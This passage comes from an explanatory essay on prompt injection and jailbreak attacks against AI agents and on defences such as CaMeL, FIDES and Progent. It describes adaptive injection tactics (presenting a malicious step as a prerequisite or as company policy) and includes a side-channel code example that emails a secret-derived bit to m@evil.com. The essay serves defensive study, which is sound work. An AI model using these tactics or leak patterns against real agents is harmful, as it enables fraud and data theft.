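Opus 5's refusals matter because the model has much of the skill needed to run an influence campaign. Anthropic tested it on two simulated social media campaigns, one to discourage voters and one to inflame social divisions. The released model refused to take part, but a version without refusal training scored 23.5 and 26.0 out of 32. Anthropic judged that a real campaign would still need substantial human direction.

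OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) describes a similar evaluation that scores an agent's actions as well as its final message, so an agent cannot pass by apologising after doing harm. Astra did better than GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI also trained Astra to refuse more borderline requests from users OpenAI has flagged as potentially high risk, so the decision still depends partly on who the user is. To guard against cyberattacks, OpenAI adds classifiers outside the model and looks for abuse afterwards.

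Users who receive a refusal can try again. SC Media's *Cisco study finds major frontier models susceptible to multi-turn prompt injection attacks* reports that Cisco tested 15 models from five companies with single harmful prompts and with conversations in which the attacker rephrased the request or built up to it gradually. The success rate rose from 2.7% for single prompts to 24.7% for conversations against GPT-5.4, from 3.6% to 16.2% against Claude Opus 4.6, and from 18.1% to 73.3% against Gemini 3 Pro. It fell from 64.9% to 30.9% against Amazon's Nova Micro, so the single-prompt scores were a poor guide even to how the models ranked in conversations. Most of these attacks were jailbreaks rather than prompt injection, as the headline calls them, because the attacker was the user and the aim was harmful output.

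A setting can matter as much as the choice of model. Attacks on Grok 4.1 Fast succeeded in 88.3% of the conversations with its reasoning mode off and in 43.5% with it on. Help Net Security's *Frontier AI models collapse under multi-turn AI attacks, Cisco finds* (2026) reports that the researchers found no differences of this kind in the public benchmarks and model documentation they reviewed. Newer models have since replaced most of those in the study.

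None of this helps much against the dishonest clerk, whose payment request has the same form as an honest one. The model may have no way to check who owns the account.

### Twelve defences against an attacker who adapts

Researchers usually test a defence against a fixed list of attacks. In October 2025, *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) showed that such a test can be weak evidence that a defence works. The researchers, who included staff of OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked twelve published defences, each with a method chosen to suit it. The original papers had reported attack success rates near zero for most of these defences.

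Their automated attackers were programs that repeatedly proposed an attack, tested it against the defended model, and used the result to write a better one. Some were language models that learned from a reward, and others generated new attacks from the most successful earlier ones. The researchers also held an online competition with more than 500 human participants. Except for Data Sentinel, the percentages below are the share of test cases in which the attacker reached the goal.

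| Defence | How it works | Result of the adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text by its source | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| RPO | Adds a prompt tuned to prevent jailbreaks | 98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model against jailbreaks | 100% |
| StruQ | Trains the model against injections | 100% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains a model for agents against injections | 96% |
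| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Classify text as safe or unsafe | Above 90% each |
| PIGuard | Classifies text as safe or unsafe | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Tests whether the text stops a model from repeating a secret word | Model did the attacker's task with over 80% accuracy |
| MELON | Runs the agent again without the user's request and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knew the method |

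Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching had let through as few as 1% of the standard attacks in AgentDojo, a set of simulated office tasks, and MetaSecAlign had let through 2%. The attack that beat Prompt Sandwiching presented the malicious action as a step required before the agent could do what the user wanted. Repeating the user's request did not help, because the model treated the malicious action as part of that request. Many of the texts that got past the filters looked like routine office policy. In one, a supposed company rule required staff to log every rescheduled meeting by deleting a certain file. A filter strict enough to catch that sentence would also block many real office documents.

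Fixed lists of attacks are misleading tests of a defence. A public list contains few attacks, and a defence can learn to recognise their wording. An attacker who finds one wording blocked will use another, so memorising typical cases is less useful here than in most areas of machine learning. Nasr and colleagues found that defences with near-zero attack success rates on public tests were often among the easiest to break. Lists also go out of date. OpenAI has dropped two of its older injection tests, and Anthropic one, because recent models score close to the maximum.

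The same problem arose years earlier with image classifiers, where attackers changed a few pixels to make a program misread a picture. Training on a stored set of altered pictures gave little protection. Generating new attacks against the model throughout its training helped, but only against the kind of attack used. GPT-Red follows this approach, which gives some reason to expect better protection from it than from StruQ or MetaSecAlign.

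Nasr and colleagues tested whether anyone could break these defences, not how much effort it would take. They gave their attackers plenty of computing power and, for the filters, the score that each attempt received. A fraudster who emails invoices to a company would not see that score. The twelve defences ran on models that are now old. The researchers also warn against comparing the percentages, because the tests differed.

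A later study, *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), tested ten defences on five models against a much more limited attacker, who learned only whether each attempt had succeeded and could make only a few attempts. Such an attacker is realistic for payment fraud, since a thief can count the payments that arrive. On an agent built on GPT-4o-mini, a small older model, PIGuard blocked every standard attack but let through 28.0% of the adapted ones. Five defences kept the success rate of standard attacks near zero on that agent, but only one of them, Progent, which restricts the agent's tool calls, also withstood the adapted attacks.

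Ma and colleagues found that the wording of the user's request mattered too. A request can state the action and all its details ("pay €18,400 to this account"), name the action but leave the details to a document ("pay this invoice"), or leave even the action open ("do what the email asks"). Attacks succeeded much more often with the last kind, where the agent has to take its instructions from the text it reads. Filters and training can make an attack harder to write, but they can't supply information that the user left out.

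### Current results for Claude Opus 5 and GPT-6 Astra

Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 5, published in July 2026, includes results from a test that the security company Gray Swan built with the British and American government institutes for AI testing and several developers. Participants in a competition looked for attacks in 28 scenarios where a successful attack would cause irreversible harm, such as leaked data or an unintended payment. The organisers kept 1,130 attacks that worked across several models, and Anthropic replayed them against its own models and those of its competitors.

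A single attempt against Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time, and an attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time. For GPT-5.6 Sol, the rates were 3.1% and 20.0%. Attackers succeeded within 15 attempts 16.5% of the time against Meta's Muse Spark, the best model from another developer.

Anthropic ran this comparison and ranked first in it. It tested its own models without their extra safeguards, while competitors' public services may have had some, so the set-up did not obviously favour Anthropic. But the test used a fixed list of attacks that people had written before Opus 5 existed, so it does not measure how well Opus 5 would resist an attacker who had studied it.

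In three further tests the attacker tried repeatedly to improve. These are the results for Opus 5 with its extended reasoning switched on:

| Setting | Scenarios and attempts | Attempts that succeeded | Scenarios broken at least once | Broken with safeguards on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Programming | 40 scenarios, 200 attempts each | 0.56% | 13 of 40 | 4 of 40 |
| Operating a computer | 14 scenarios, 200 attempts each | 0.54% | 1 of 14 | 1 of 14 |
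| Operating a browser | 129 scenarios, 10 attempts each | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

The safeguards were the probes in the first two tests and auto mode in the third. In the programming test, Gray Swan's automated attacker had practised on the same scenarios but against earlier models, so it was probably weaker than one that had practised on Opus 5. But it also had an advantage over real attackers, who, as Anthropic points out, rarely know the exact set-up they are attacking and would be more likely to be discovered if they made 200 attempts.

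Opus 5 improved greatly on Opus 4.8, against which 31.5% of attempts succeeded in the browser test. Other Anthropic models did better than Opus 5 in some settings, however. Without safeguards, Sonnet 5 was more robust in the browser, where 0.93% of attempts succeeded. Mythos 5 was slightly more robust in programming, where 0.45% succeeded, but 29.7% succeeded against it in the browser. A model's programming score is therefore a poor guide to its robustness as a browser agent.

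In September 2026, OpenAI reported that GPT-6 Astra resisted indirect injection in 99.79% of queries, up from 96.23%, in the company's own test with GPT-Red as the attacker. The model resisted direct attempts to override higher-ranking instructions 99.99% of the time. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) relays OpenAI's figures for GPT-6 Sol, a model in the same family that did about as well on direct attacks but less well on indirect ones.

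Astra's failure rate of 0.21% isn't directly comparable with the 0.2% for Opus 5 in the Gray Swan test, because the attackers, scenarios and methods of counting were different. Such differences can matter a lot. OpenAI's test and the Gray Swan test ranked the three GPT-5.6 models in opposite orders. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that in OpenAI's test, indirect attacks succeeded 3.77% of the time against Sol, 3.32% against Terra and 2.94% against Luna. In the Gray Swan test, Sol was the most robust of the three and Luna the least, with attack success rates of 20.0% and 43.9% within 15 attempts.

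VentureBeat compared four developers' disclosures as of spring 2026 and found that no two matched. It also noted that Anthropic's lowest figures apply to its own products. A company that connects its invoice agent directly to the model does not get those products' safeguards, though it can add its own.

### What happens when the attacker tries again

An attacker can send more than one email. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of *k* attempts succeeds is:

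$$P_k = 1 - (1-p)^k$$

The term $(1-p)^k$ is the chance that every attempt fails. For Opus 5 in the Gray Swan test, *p* is 0.002, so the chance that at least one of 15 attempts succeeds would be 1 − 0.998¹⁵, or about 3.0%. The reported figure was 2.0%. Other published results are also lower than the formula gives, including an older one for Claude Opus 4.5 in The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

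| Model | One attempt | Number of attempts | If attempts were independent | Reported |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 15 | 37.6% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38.2% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99.2% | 63% |

The gap probably arises because some scenarios are much weaker than others. Rounding does not explain it, because the formula would give 2.2% even if the true single-attempt rate for Opus 5 were 0.15%.

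Suppose a company's agent handles ten kinds of document. No attack works on nine of them, but one attack in five works on the tenth, scanned delivery notes. The average success rate is 2%, so the formula gives an 18% chance of at least one success in ten attempts on one kind of document picked at random. The true chance is 9%, because nine times out of ten the attacker has picked a kind on which no attack works. But an attacker who knows about the delivery notes has an 89% chance of success within ten attempts.

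The tests of Opus 5 show this pattern. In the computer test, about 15 of 2,800 attempts (0.54%) succeeded. All of them were in one of the 14 scenarios, where about 7.5% of attempts succeeded. If the scenarios had been equally vulnerable, about nine would have had at least one success. In the browser test, about 48 attempts succeeded, all in 11 of the 129 scenarios. In those 11, the attacker succeeded in more than four attempts out of ten. A company whose agent does a task like one of those 11 faces a far higher risk than the 3.70% average suggests.

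Fifteen failed attacks on one scenario are therefore some evidence that the sixteenth will fail too. This gives the company limited reassurance, because an attacker can switch to another document type or send the same invoice to a thousand companies in the hope that one is vulnerable. A low average success rate does help against attackers who pick targets at random and give up early.

For anyone who expects a persistent attacker, the attack success rate over many attempts is more useful than the average, but it should be reported with the setting in which it was measured. VentureBeat reported that Claude Opus 4.6, from February 2026, withstood all 200 attempts in a restricted programming environment. When the model operated a computer through its graphical interface, the attack success rate was 17.8% on the first attempt and 78.6% by the 200th.

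### The claim that browser injection may be solved

The Decoder published *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* in response to the result of 0 out of 129. The article notes that the zero applies only with auto mode on.

A test of this size can also record no successful attacks even when some would work. If 2% of comparable pages could defeat the agent, a random sample of 129 would include none of them about 7% of the time. The 129 were also a curated set of attacks written by professional testers, not a random sample of the web. Someone who studies one particular product may find a method that no test set contains. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) reports that a test of auto mode in Claude Code, commissioned by Anthropic, recorded no successful attacks in 72 scenarios, and that the security researcher Johann Rehberger then designed an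 attack that worked in roughly 60% to 80% of a small number of attempts.

Bruce Schneier, a well-known writer on computer security, drew a more limited conclusion from the same system card in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026). He holds that preventing prompt injection is impossible in general, but that developers are getting much better at blocking it in specific cases. One of his readers objected that the paper behind the impossibility claim was about jailbreaks, and that a different kind of model might keep trusted and untrusted text apart. The objection is reasonable about that paper. The argument from contextual integrity is more relevant, but it also depends on what the agent can check.

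OpenAI had taken a similar position in December 2025. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025), a post about its browser agent, described automated attacks as a way to find and repair weaknesses before criminals use them. Fortune (2025) quoted the company's view that injection, like scams and social engineering, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". The comparison with scams is apt because fraud has not been eliminated, but banks have reduced it enough that people still use banks, and they have procedures for the cases that get through.

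The test results don't refute Schneier and OpenAI, who were writing about every attack that anyone might devise, while The Decoder was writing about one set of tests. The results are good evidence that an attacker now needs more skill or luck than a year earlier. That may be enough protection for an agent that summarises web pages, but an agent that can make payments needs more, because even a rare successful attack could cost €18,400.

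### The Defense Trilemma

*The Defense Trilemma* (Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues, 2026) proves that a wrapper, a program that rewrites each prompt before the model reads it, can never be a perfect defence. A perfect wrapper would turn dangerous prompts into safe ones and leave safe prompts alone.

Let *X* be the set of all possible prompts, and let *f*(*x*) measure how badly the model behaves when it receives prompt *x*. A prompt is safe if *f*(*x*) is below a threshold τ. The wrapper is a function *D* that turns each prompt into another. The theorem concerns three properties:

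- *D* is continuous, which means that similar prompts lead to similar rewrites.
- *D* preserves utility, which means that *D*(*x*) = *x* for every safe prompt.
- *D* is complete, which means that *f*(*D*(*x*)) < τ for every prompt.

No wrapper can have all three if *f* is also continuous, both safe and unsafe prompts exist, and the space of prompts is connected. Connected roughly means that the space is in one piece, with no gap between the safe prompts and the rest.

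For example, suppose the prompts lie on a line from 0 to 1, *f*(*x*) = *x*, and the threshold is 0.5. The wrapper must leave every prompt below 0.5 unchanged, including 0.4, 0.49 and 0.499, because they are all safe. Since it is continuous, it cannot jump at 0.5, so it must leave 0.5 unchanged too, even though 0.5 is unsafe because it is not below the threshold. The general proof uses the same idea, since the prompts that *D* leaves unchanged form a closed set, meaning one that includes its edge, whereas the set of safe prompts does not include its edge.

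A prompt exactly at the threshold is only barely unsafe, so this result alone is not very alarming. Bhatt and colleagues then assume limits on how fast *f* and *D* can change from one prompt to the next, which means the wrapper can reduce the danger only slightly near the unchanged point. If the danger also rises steeply enough in some direction, a whole region of prompts remains unsafe after rewriting. They report evidence of such steep rises in two of the three models they tested. A computer program has checked the proofs, so a logical error is unlikely, but the assumptions may not fit real systems.

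The assumptions are restrictive. The connected space is a mathematical idealisation, because prompts consist of separate tokens, with no smooth path from one prompt to another. The paper includes a version for finite sets of prompts, in which a complete wrapper that leaves safe prompts alone must turn at least two different prompts into the same one. This loses information, but the loss is harmless if the wrapper replaces a malicious email with a blank page.

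The theorem also does not cover most current defences, as Bhatt and colleagues point out. It does not apply to training the model, changing its design, filtering its output or human review. Nor does it apply to a classifier that rejects a prompt outright, because a jump from "let through" to "block" is not continuous. In the example above, a filter that blocks every prompt where *f* is 0.5 or higher is complete and leaves every safe prompt unchanged. However, the filter requires the value of *f* for each prompt, and the text of an email about a new bank account is not enough to determine it.

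## Limiting what a deceived agent can do

Even the best-trained models sometimes follow an injected instruction, so another family of defences assumes that someone will eventually fool the model. Software outside the model decides which tool calls take effect. If a deceived model requests a payment to a thief, this software can block the request before it reaches the bank. Narisetty and colleagues trace these defences to computer science ideas from the 1960s and 1970s.

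### The older ideas

Least privilege means giving a program only the permissions its task requires. To pay one invoice, the agent has to read the mailbox, look up a supplier and make a payment, so the harness can withhold the tool that sends email.

A capability is an unforgeable token that identifies an object and gives its holder certain rights over it. If Hardy's compiler had used capabilities, it could not have overwritten the billing file, because the user would have had to supply a token for that file and had none. The harness could give the invoice agent a token for paying the paper supplier up to €18,400, instead of a tool that accepts any account number.

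A reference monitor is a component outside the model that checks every tool call against a policy before the call takes effect. James Anderson's 1972 study for the US Air Force set three requirements: the monitor must always run, nobody may be able to tamper with it, and it must be small enough to verify. A short program that compares the account number in each payment call with the supplier list could meet all three. It would fail the first if the agent could also order payments by emailing the bank, the second if the agent could edit the supplier list, and the third if another language model made the comparison.

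Kenneth Biba's integrity model, from 1977, has two rules. A program that reads less trusted data drops to that data's trust level, and a program may not write to anything above its own level. Once the invoice agent has read a supplier's PDF, it drops to the supplier's level and may no longer order a payment. This would prevent the theft but also stop the agent from doing its job. Newer designs try to keep Biba's protection while letting the agent do its work.

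Information-flow control attaches a label to each piece of data and carries the label along as programs copy and combine the data. The simplest integrity labels are "trusted" and "untrusted", and anything derived from both is untrusted. Labels can also list people, as Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, explain. If *z* is a text that combines *x* and *y*, then:

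$$\mathrm{readers}(z) = \mathrm{readers}(x) \cap \mathrm{readers}(y), \qquad \mathrm{writers}(z) = \mathrm{writers}(x) \cup \mathrm{writers}(y)$$

When an agent combines data from two sources, only people allowed to read both sources may read the result, and anyone who could have written either one may have influenced it. If the agent copies an account number from a supplier's PDF, the supplier therefore still counts as a possible writer of that number, no matter how many steps later the agent uses it.

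### Two models instead of one

Biba's rule interferes with the task because the same model reads the invoice and orders the payment. In April 2023, Simon Willison proposed giving these jobs to separate models. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) recounts his proposal, in which a privileged model takes the user's request and can call tools but never sees untrusted text. A quarantined model reads that text but has no tools. It stores its results under names such as `$email-summary-1`, which the privileged model uses without seeing the results themselves.

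If the supplier's PDF contains a hidden request to email the company's contracts to a stranger, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model cannot send email. But a false account number hidden in the PDF still reaches the bank, because the quarantined model stores it as `$account` and the privileged model passes `$account` on without seeing the number. Willison's pattern protects the choice of actions but leaves the values in them open to manipulation, a flaw that researchers at Google DeepMind pointed out when they introduced their own system, CaMeL.

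### A poisoned invoice in CaMeL

CaMeL (short for CApabilities for MachinE Learning) also records where each value came from. The privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted version of Python, and a purpose-built interpreter runs it. For a request to pay the paper supplier's latest invoice, the program might be:

```python
email = get_latest_email(sender="paper supplier")
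bill = query_quarantined_llm("Find the amount and account number", email)
create_payment(payee="paper supplier", amount=bill.amount, account=bill.account)
```

If the PDF contains the attacker's account number in white type, the run goes like this:

1. The privileged model writes the program from the clerk's request. It has not seen the email, so the hidden sentence cannot add a step.
2. The interpreter fetches the email and tags it as coming from an outside sender.
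3. The quarantined model reads the PDF and returns the attacker's account number. The interpreter gives `bill` the same tag as the email, because it derived one from the other.
4. Before it calls the payment tool, the interpreter checks the company's policy, under which account numbers must come from the supplier list. This one came from the email, so the interpreter blocks the payment or asks the clerk to approve it.

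The check blocks the order before it reaches the bank. It does not rely on recognising an attack, so it would also block payment of a genuine invoice if the program tried to use the account number printed on it. The program should therefore take the account number from the supplier list.

That is simple if the clerk has named the supplier. If the clerk asks the agent to pay whatever has come in, the program has to look up the entry using the supplier's name from the email. Strict tracking then marks the listed account number as untrusted too, because the email determined which entry the program fetched. The company has to write an exception that accepts any account number on the list. With that exception, a forged invoice can't cause a payment to a stranger, but it can still cause a payment to the wrong supplier.

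According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo, against 84% for an undefended agent, and stopped every attack of the kind it was built to stop. It used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. The success rate fell much further on financial tasks. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* that turning on the policy checks halved CaMeL's success rate on AgentDojo's banking tasks.

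Someone also has to write the policies and keep them up to date. CaMeL's developers acknowledge that frequent requests for approval tire users. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) criticises CaMeL's use of Python, because some of the language's features make programs hard to analyse before they run, and recommends a simpler language designed for security. However, the design can improve privacy. If the quarantined model is a small one running on the company's own computers, the provider of the privileged model never sees the invoices.

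### Labels in FIDES

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, also uses two models but hides less from the privileged one, called the planner. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares the label of each field with the label of the conversation so far. It hides a field in a variable only if showing it to the planner would make the conversation less trusted. The planner might see an email's date and verified sender address, but only variable names in place of the subject and body.

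Sometimes the planner needs information from the hidden text to choose its next step, such as whether an email contains an invoice. FIDES can send that question to the quarantined model and restrict the answer to yes or no. An attacker can make the answer wrong, but a yes or no cannot contain an instruction or an account number. The company can allow such answers to influence payments.

FIDES checks tool calls against two kinds of policy. The first allows a consequential action, such as a payment, only if the call and its arguments derive from trusted data. The second allows a message to be sent only if every recipient is permitted to read all the information in it. By default, FIDES treats the agent's answers to its own user as harmless and does not check them. This would leave a gap for attacks like EchoLeak, which sent stolen information out through an image address in Copilot's answer.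 A developer can extend the checks to answers.

In tests with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its policy checks off, and none with them on. These counts leave out cases that the researchers judged AgentDojo had scored wrongly. With the checks on, AgentDojo itself had counted three successes. The checks also stopped a lot of legitimate work. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed when nobody was attacking:

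| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

FIDES recovered some of the performance that an ordinary agent lost to the checks, except in travel, where the planner often misused the variables. A stronger model, o1, handled the variables better and raised the travel score to 68%. Many of the banking failures were intended, because the task told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. Costa and colleagues classify 43.8% of the banking tasks, compared with 5.0% of the workspace tasks, as ones in which the right actions depend on what the agent reads. "Pay whatever has come in" is also such a task.

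### Rules in Progent

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) can protect an existing agent without changes to its internal design. It places a reference monitor between the agent and its tools. The monitor checks each tool call against a policy, which is a list of rules, and blocks any call that no rule allows. Each rule contains the name of a tool and conditions on its arguments. For example, a rule may allow Slack messages only to Alice.

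Writing a policy by hand for every request would take too long, so a language model writes the first one from the user's request, before the agent has read anything untrusted. The same model can propose changes as the agent learns more. If $A(P)$ is the set of tool calls that policy *P* allows, a logic solver checks whether a proposed policy *P′* satisfies

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

When the model proposes a change to an agent's permissions, Progent applies it automatically if it adds no permissions. Otherwise the change requires approval, either from a person or under a setting chosen in advance. A poisoned email may lead the model to propose a new permission, but the permission does not take effect without that approval.

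A user who asks an agent to pay whatever invoices have come in doesn't specify the payees, so the initial policy must either allow payments to anyone or block all payments until the agent has read the invoices. If it blocks them, the model proposes a new permission after reading the attacker's text, and whoever approves it has to notice that the account number is wrong.

Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo with GPT-4o from 39.9% to 1.0% and largely preserved the agent's ability to do its tasks. In that test, Progent approved every new permission automatically, to simulate a careless user. When the first policy was never updated, the rate was 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and every new permission, no attack succeeded. Only 6% of the updates added permissions, so this reviewer had few to consider. On a second benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%,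 and most of the attacks that still succeeded used malicious tools with names and descriptions similar to those of useful ones.

Progent interferes less with ordinary work than FIDES partly because it checks the arguments of a call without tracking where they came from. If a rule allows payments of any amount to a listed supplier, Progent cannot detect whether the amount came from the clerk or from a forged invoice.

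*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) combines both kinds of check. Before each tool call, the system looks for paths from untrusted data to the action and checks that the user's request authorises the effect. Across eight benchmarks, the protected agents' task completion rate was at most three percentage points lower than that of undefended agents. However, the tested version could still allow an authorised call that the path check had flagged for blocking, so the paper's full mathematical guarantee does not cover that version.

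### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

A company can also avoid dangerous combinations of permissions. Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside world. A stranger can get an agent with all three to read the private data and send it out. Removing any one of them prevents that theft. The invoice agent has all three, since it reads contracts, opens suppliers' emails and can send email.

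A November post in the blog series *Prompt injection* (Willison, 2025) discusses Meta's "Agents Rule of Two". Under this rule, an agent working without supervision should have at most two of these properties in one session: it processes untrusted input, it can reach sensitive systems or private data, and it can change things or communicate externally. If an agent needs all three, a person or some other reliable check should approve its actions. The rule is broader than the trifecta because it includes changes, such as payments, that can do harm without revealing private data.

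Both rules are easy to apply before anyone writes code, but they are crude. An agent that reads public comments and posts replies in the company's name has only two of Meta's properties, yet a stranger could still make it post something damaging. Splitting the invoice agent in two helps only if the half that reads email can't send free text to the half that makes payments, because free text can carry an injected instruction.

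*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) describes a paper with a similar approach by 11 researchers from IBM, ETH Zurich, Google, Microsoft and elsewhere. The paper proposes restricting agents so that they cannot carry out arbitrary tasks. This is a serious loss for a general assistant, but a much smaller one for an agent that only has to pay known suppliers for goods the company has ordered.

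### Wrong labels and false values

A monitor that works as designed can still let a harmful action through if data starts with the wrong label. Most systems treat whatever the user types as trusted. If the clerk pastes a new account number from an email into the request, the monitor will treat the number as trusted too. Narisetty and colleagues add that the deployed form of FIDES treats unlabeled data as trusted. Correct labels do protect against forged records like those of Choi and colleagues, as long as software labels each field before the model reads it.

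A permitted field can also contain a false value. A rule that fixes the account number does not prevent an attacker from changing the amount from €18,400 to €81,400. The agent usually takes the amount from the invoice. The monitor could compare it with the purchase order, but this works only if the purchase order is correct and the supplier cannot alter it. A supplier who bills for the full order but delivers less would still pass that check, unless the monitor also checks the delivery records.

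Systems that check only tool calls do not block misleading text. If a poisoned contract causes the agent to tell the clerk that a payment is overdue, the clerk may order the payment in good faith. The request then comes from a principal, so the monitor would allow it.

Permissions may also be broader than the agent's purpose. In *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents*, Copty, Haiby and colleagues (2026) point out that an action can stay within the agent's permissions and show no sign of an attack, yet still conflict with the purpose the organisation gave the agent. For example, the invoice agent might pay every bill on the day it arrives when company policy is to wait 30 days. They build a profile of each agent's purpose from company policy, the agent's role and its configuration. On their own benchmark of 887 examples, adding the profile raised a classifier's score from 45% to 79%, on a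 measure that counts both missed cases and false alarms. The classifier still makes too many mistakes to replace fixed rules, though it can supplement them.

The policy itself may be wrong. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that Progent's guarantees depend on complete and correct policies, which are hard to write by hand. It also notes that poisoned tool results may lead the update mechanism to relax those policies. Progent's solver can prove that a new policy adds a permission, but not that the permission is a bad idea.

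### Side channels

Information can also leak through what a program does, even if the program never copies the secret itself. Suppose a program is to email an outsider only if the company's bank balance is above a certain threshold. CaMeL blocks this because the secret balance determines whether the email goes out. Garby and colleagues show how a classic trick gets around the check. In outline, it works like this:

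```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when the program assigns a value to it after testing a secret. If the balance is high, the program changes `tmp`, which CaMeL marks, and then skips the line that would change `rich`. Because `rich` stays true and unmarked, the email goes out. If the balance is low, the program leaves `tmp` alone, sets `rich` to false and sends nothing. The outsider can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether an email arrives.

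An outsider would have trouble getting CaMeL to run this program, because the privileged model writes its code from the clerk's request alone. The example shows a gap in the tracking more than a ready-made attack. However, CaMeL's developers demonstrated two side channels that work against the system, including one in which the attacker triggers a program error.

Garby and colleagues found a further leak in the way CaMeL retries failed programs. Whether a policy check stopped a run can reveal one yes-or-no fact about a secret. One such fact is rarely useful, but repeated runs can reveal more. Twenty well-chosen yes-or-no questions are enough to find any balance below €1 million to the nearest euro.

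FIDES deliberately does not try to prevent leaks of this kind. To rule them out, it would have to block almost every outgoing message once the agent had called a tool that might read something confidential. Garby and colleagues instead designed a small programming language in which every value carries a label. They used a proof checker to verify that secret data in a program cannot influence its public results, except by affecting whether the program finishes. An agent written in this language resisted manipulation in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did when run without its policy checks. The proof holds only if the labels are right. Programmers can also override integrity labels with an explicit command, which makes the exceptions easy to find.

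### Permissions after a context summary

Progent takes the latest user message in a conversation as the user's request. This can go wrong when a harness compacts a long conversation into a summary. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, recorded 1,108 automatic summaries in Claude Code and Codex. The harness inserted every summary as a user message, so Progent could treat an attacker's words in a summary as the user's request.

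Progent's own integrations avoid some of this by writing the first policy once per session, but the user may then lack permissions for later tasks. Agents completed the second task in 7 of 60 sessions when the policy was fixed at the first request, compared with 41 when each request got a new policy. Fei and colleagues therefore tested Progent with a new policy for each request.

In one experiment, the user gave the agent a landlord's account number and asked what a notice said. The attacker had written the notice and included a different account number as plain data. After the harness summarised the conversation, the user asked the agent to pay the rent. Policies that GPT-4o wrote from the summary allowed payment to the attacker's account in 91% of cases, and those that GPT-5.5 wrote allowed it in 59%. When either model worked from the user's own messages, the policy never allowed it.

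An agent does not always make a payment that its policy permits. When Fei and colleagues let an agent act under the policies based on summaries, it paid the attacker in 33 of 80 runs. Of 410 banking policies written from summaries that omitted the attacker's account number, 78 still allowed the attacker's transfer, often because they did not restrict who could be paid.

The summarising models were good at spotting injected instructions. Two recent models flagged them in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept the attacker's account number or address, but they rarely flagged false data. The paper explains this with a theorem about any system that judges text without knowing who wrote it. Let $p_L$ be the probability that the system allows a payment when the record naming the account is genuine, and $p_A$ the probability when an attacker forged it. Then:

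$$p_L - p_A \le \mathrm{TV}(P_L, P_A)$$

$P_L$ and $P_A$ are the probability distributions of the text the system reads in the two cases. TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart they are, from 0 for identical distributions to 1 for completely distinguishable ones. If an attacker can write a notice exactly as a landlord would, the distance is 0, and the system will allow the false account as often as the true one. The argument resembles Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's, but it applies to a specific step in products people already use.

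Fei and colleagues propose giving the agent the summary and the policy writer only the user's messages, which the harness tags cryptographically on arrival and carries over unchanged. If a message is missing, altered or out of order, the policy writer receives nothing and the policy allows no tool calls. In 40 attacked runs with this protection, no attacker's action succeeded while the agent read the summary. The agent completed 19 of the users' tasks when the harness supplied the summary as a tool result, compared with 27 in the original runs without a summary.

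These were replayed benchmark sessions, and nobody had yet built the full design into a product. In October 2026, OpenAI made a simpler change to a reviewer in Codex, which now attributes summaries to the assistant instead of the user. Neither measure helps if the user says "pay the account in the notice", because the user's words contain no account number to check the payment against.

CaMeL depended less on the summary because it attaches permissions to individual values. The attacker's action still succeeded in 3 of 36 banking runs after a summary.

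### Adaptive attacks on deterministic checks

Narisetty and colleagues warn that CaMeL, FIDES and Progent have been tested mainly against fixed lists of attacks, as were, at first, the filters and training methods that adaptive attackers later broke. In June 2026 they published an independent test of Progent using an attack written to defeat it. The injected text presented the malicious action as a necessary step that someone had already authorised, to try to get Progent's policy-writing model to allow it.

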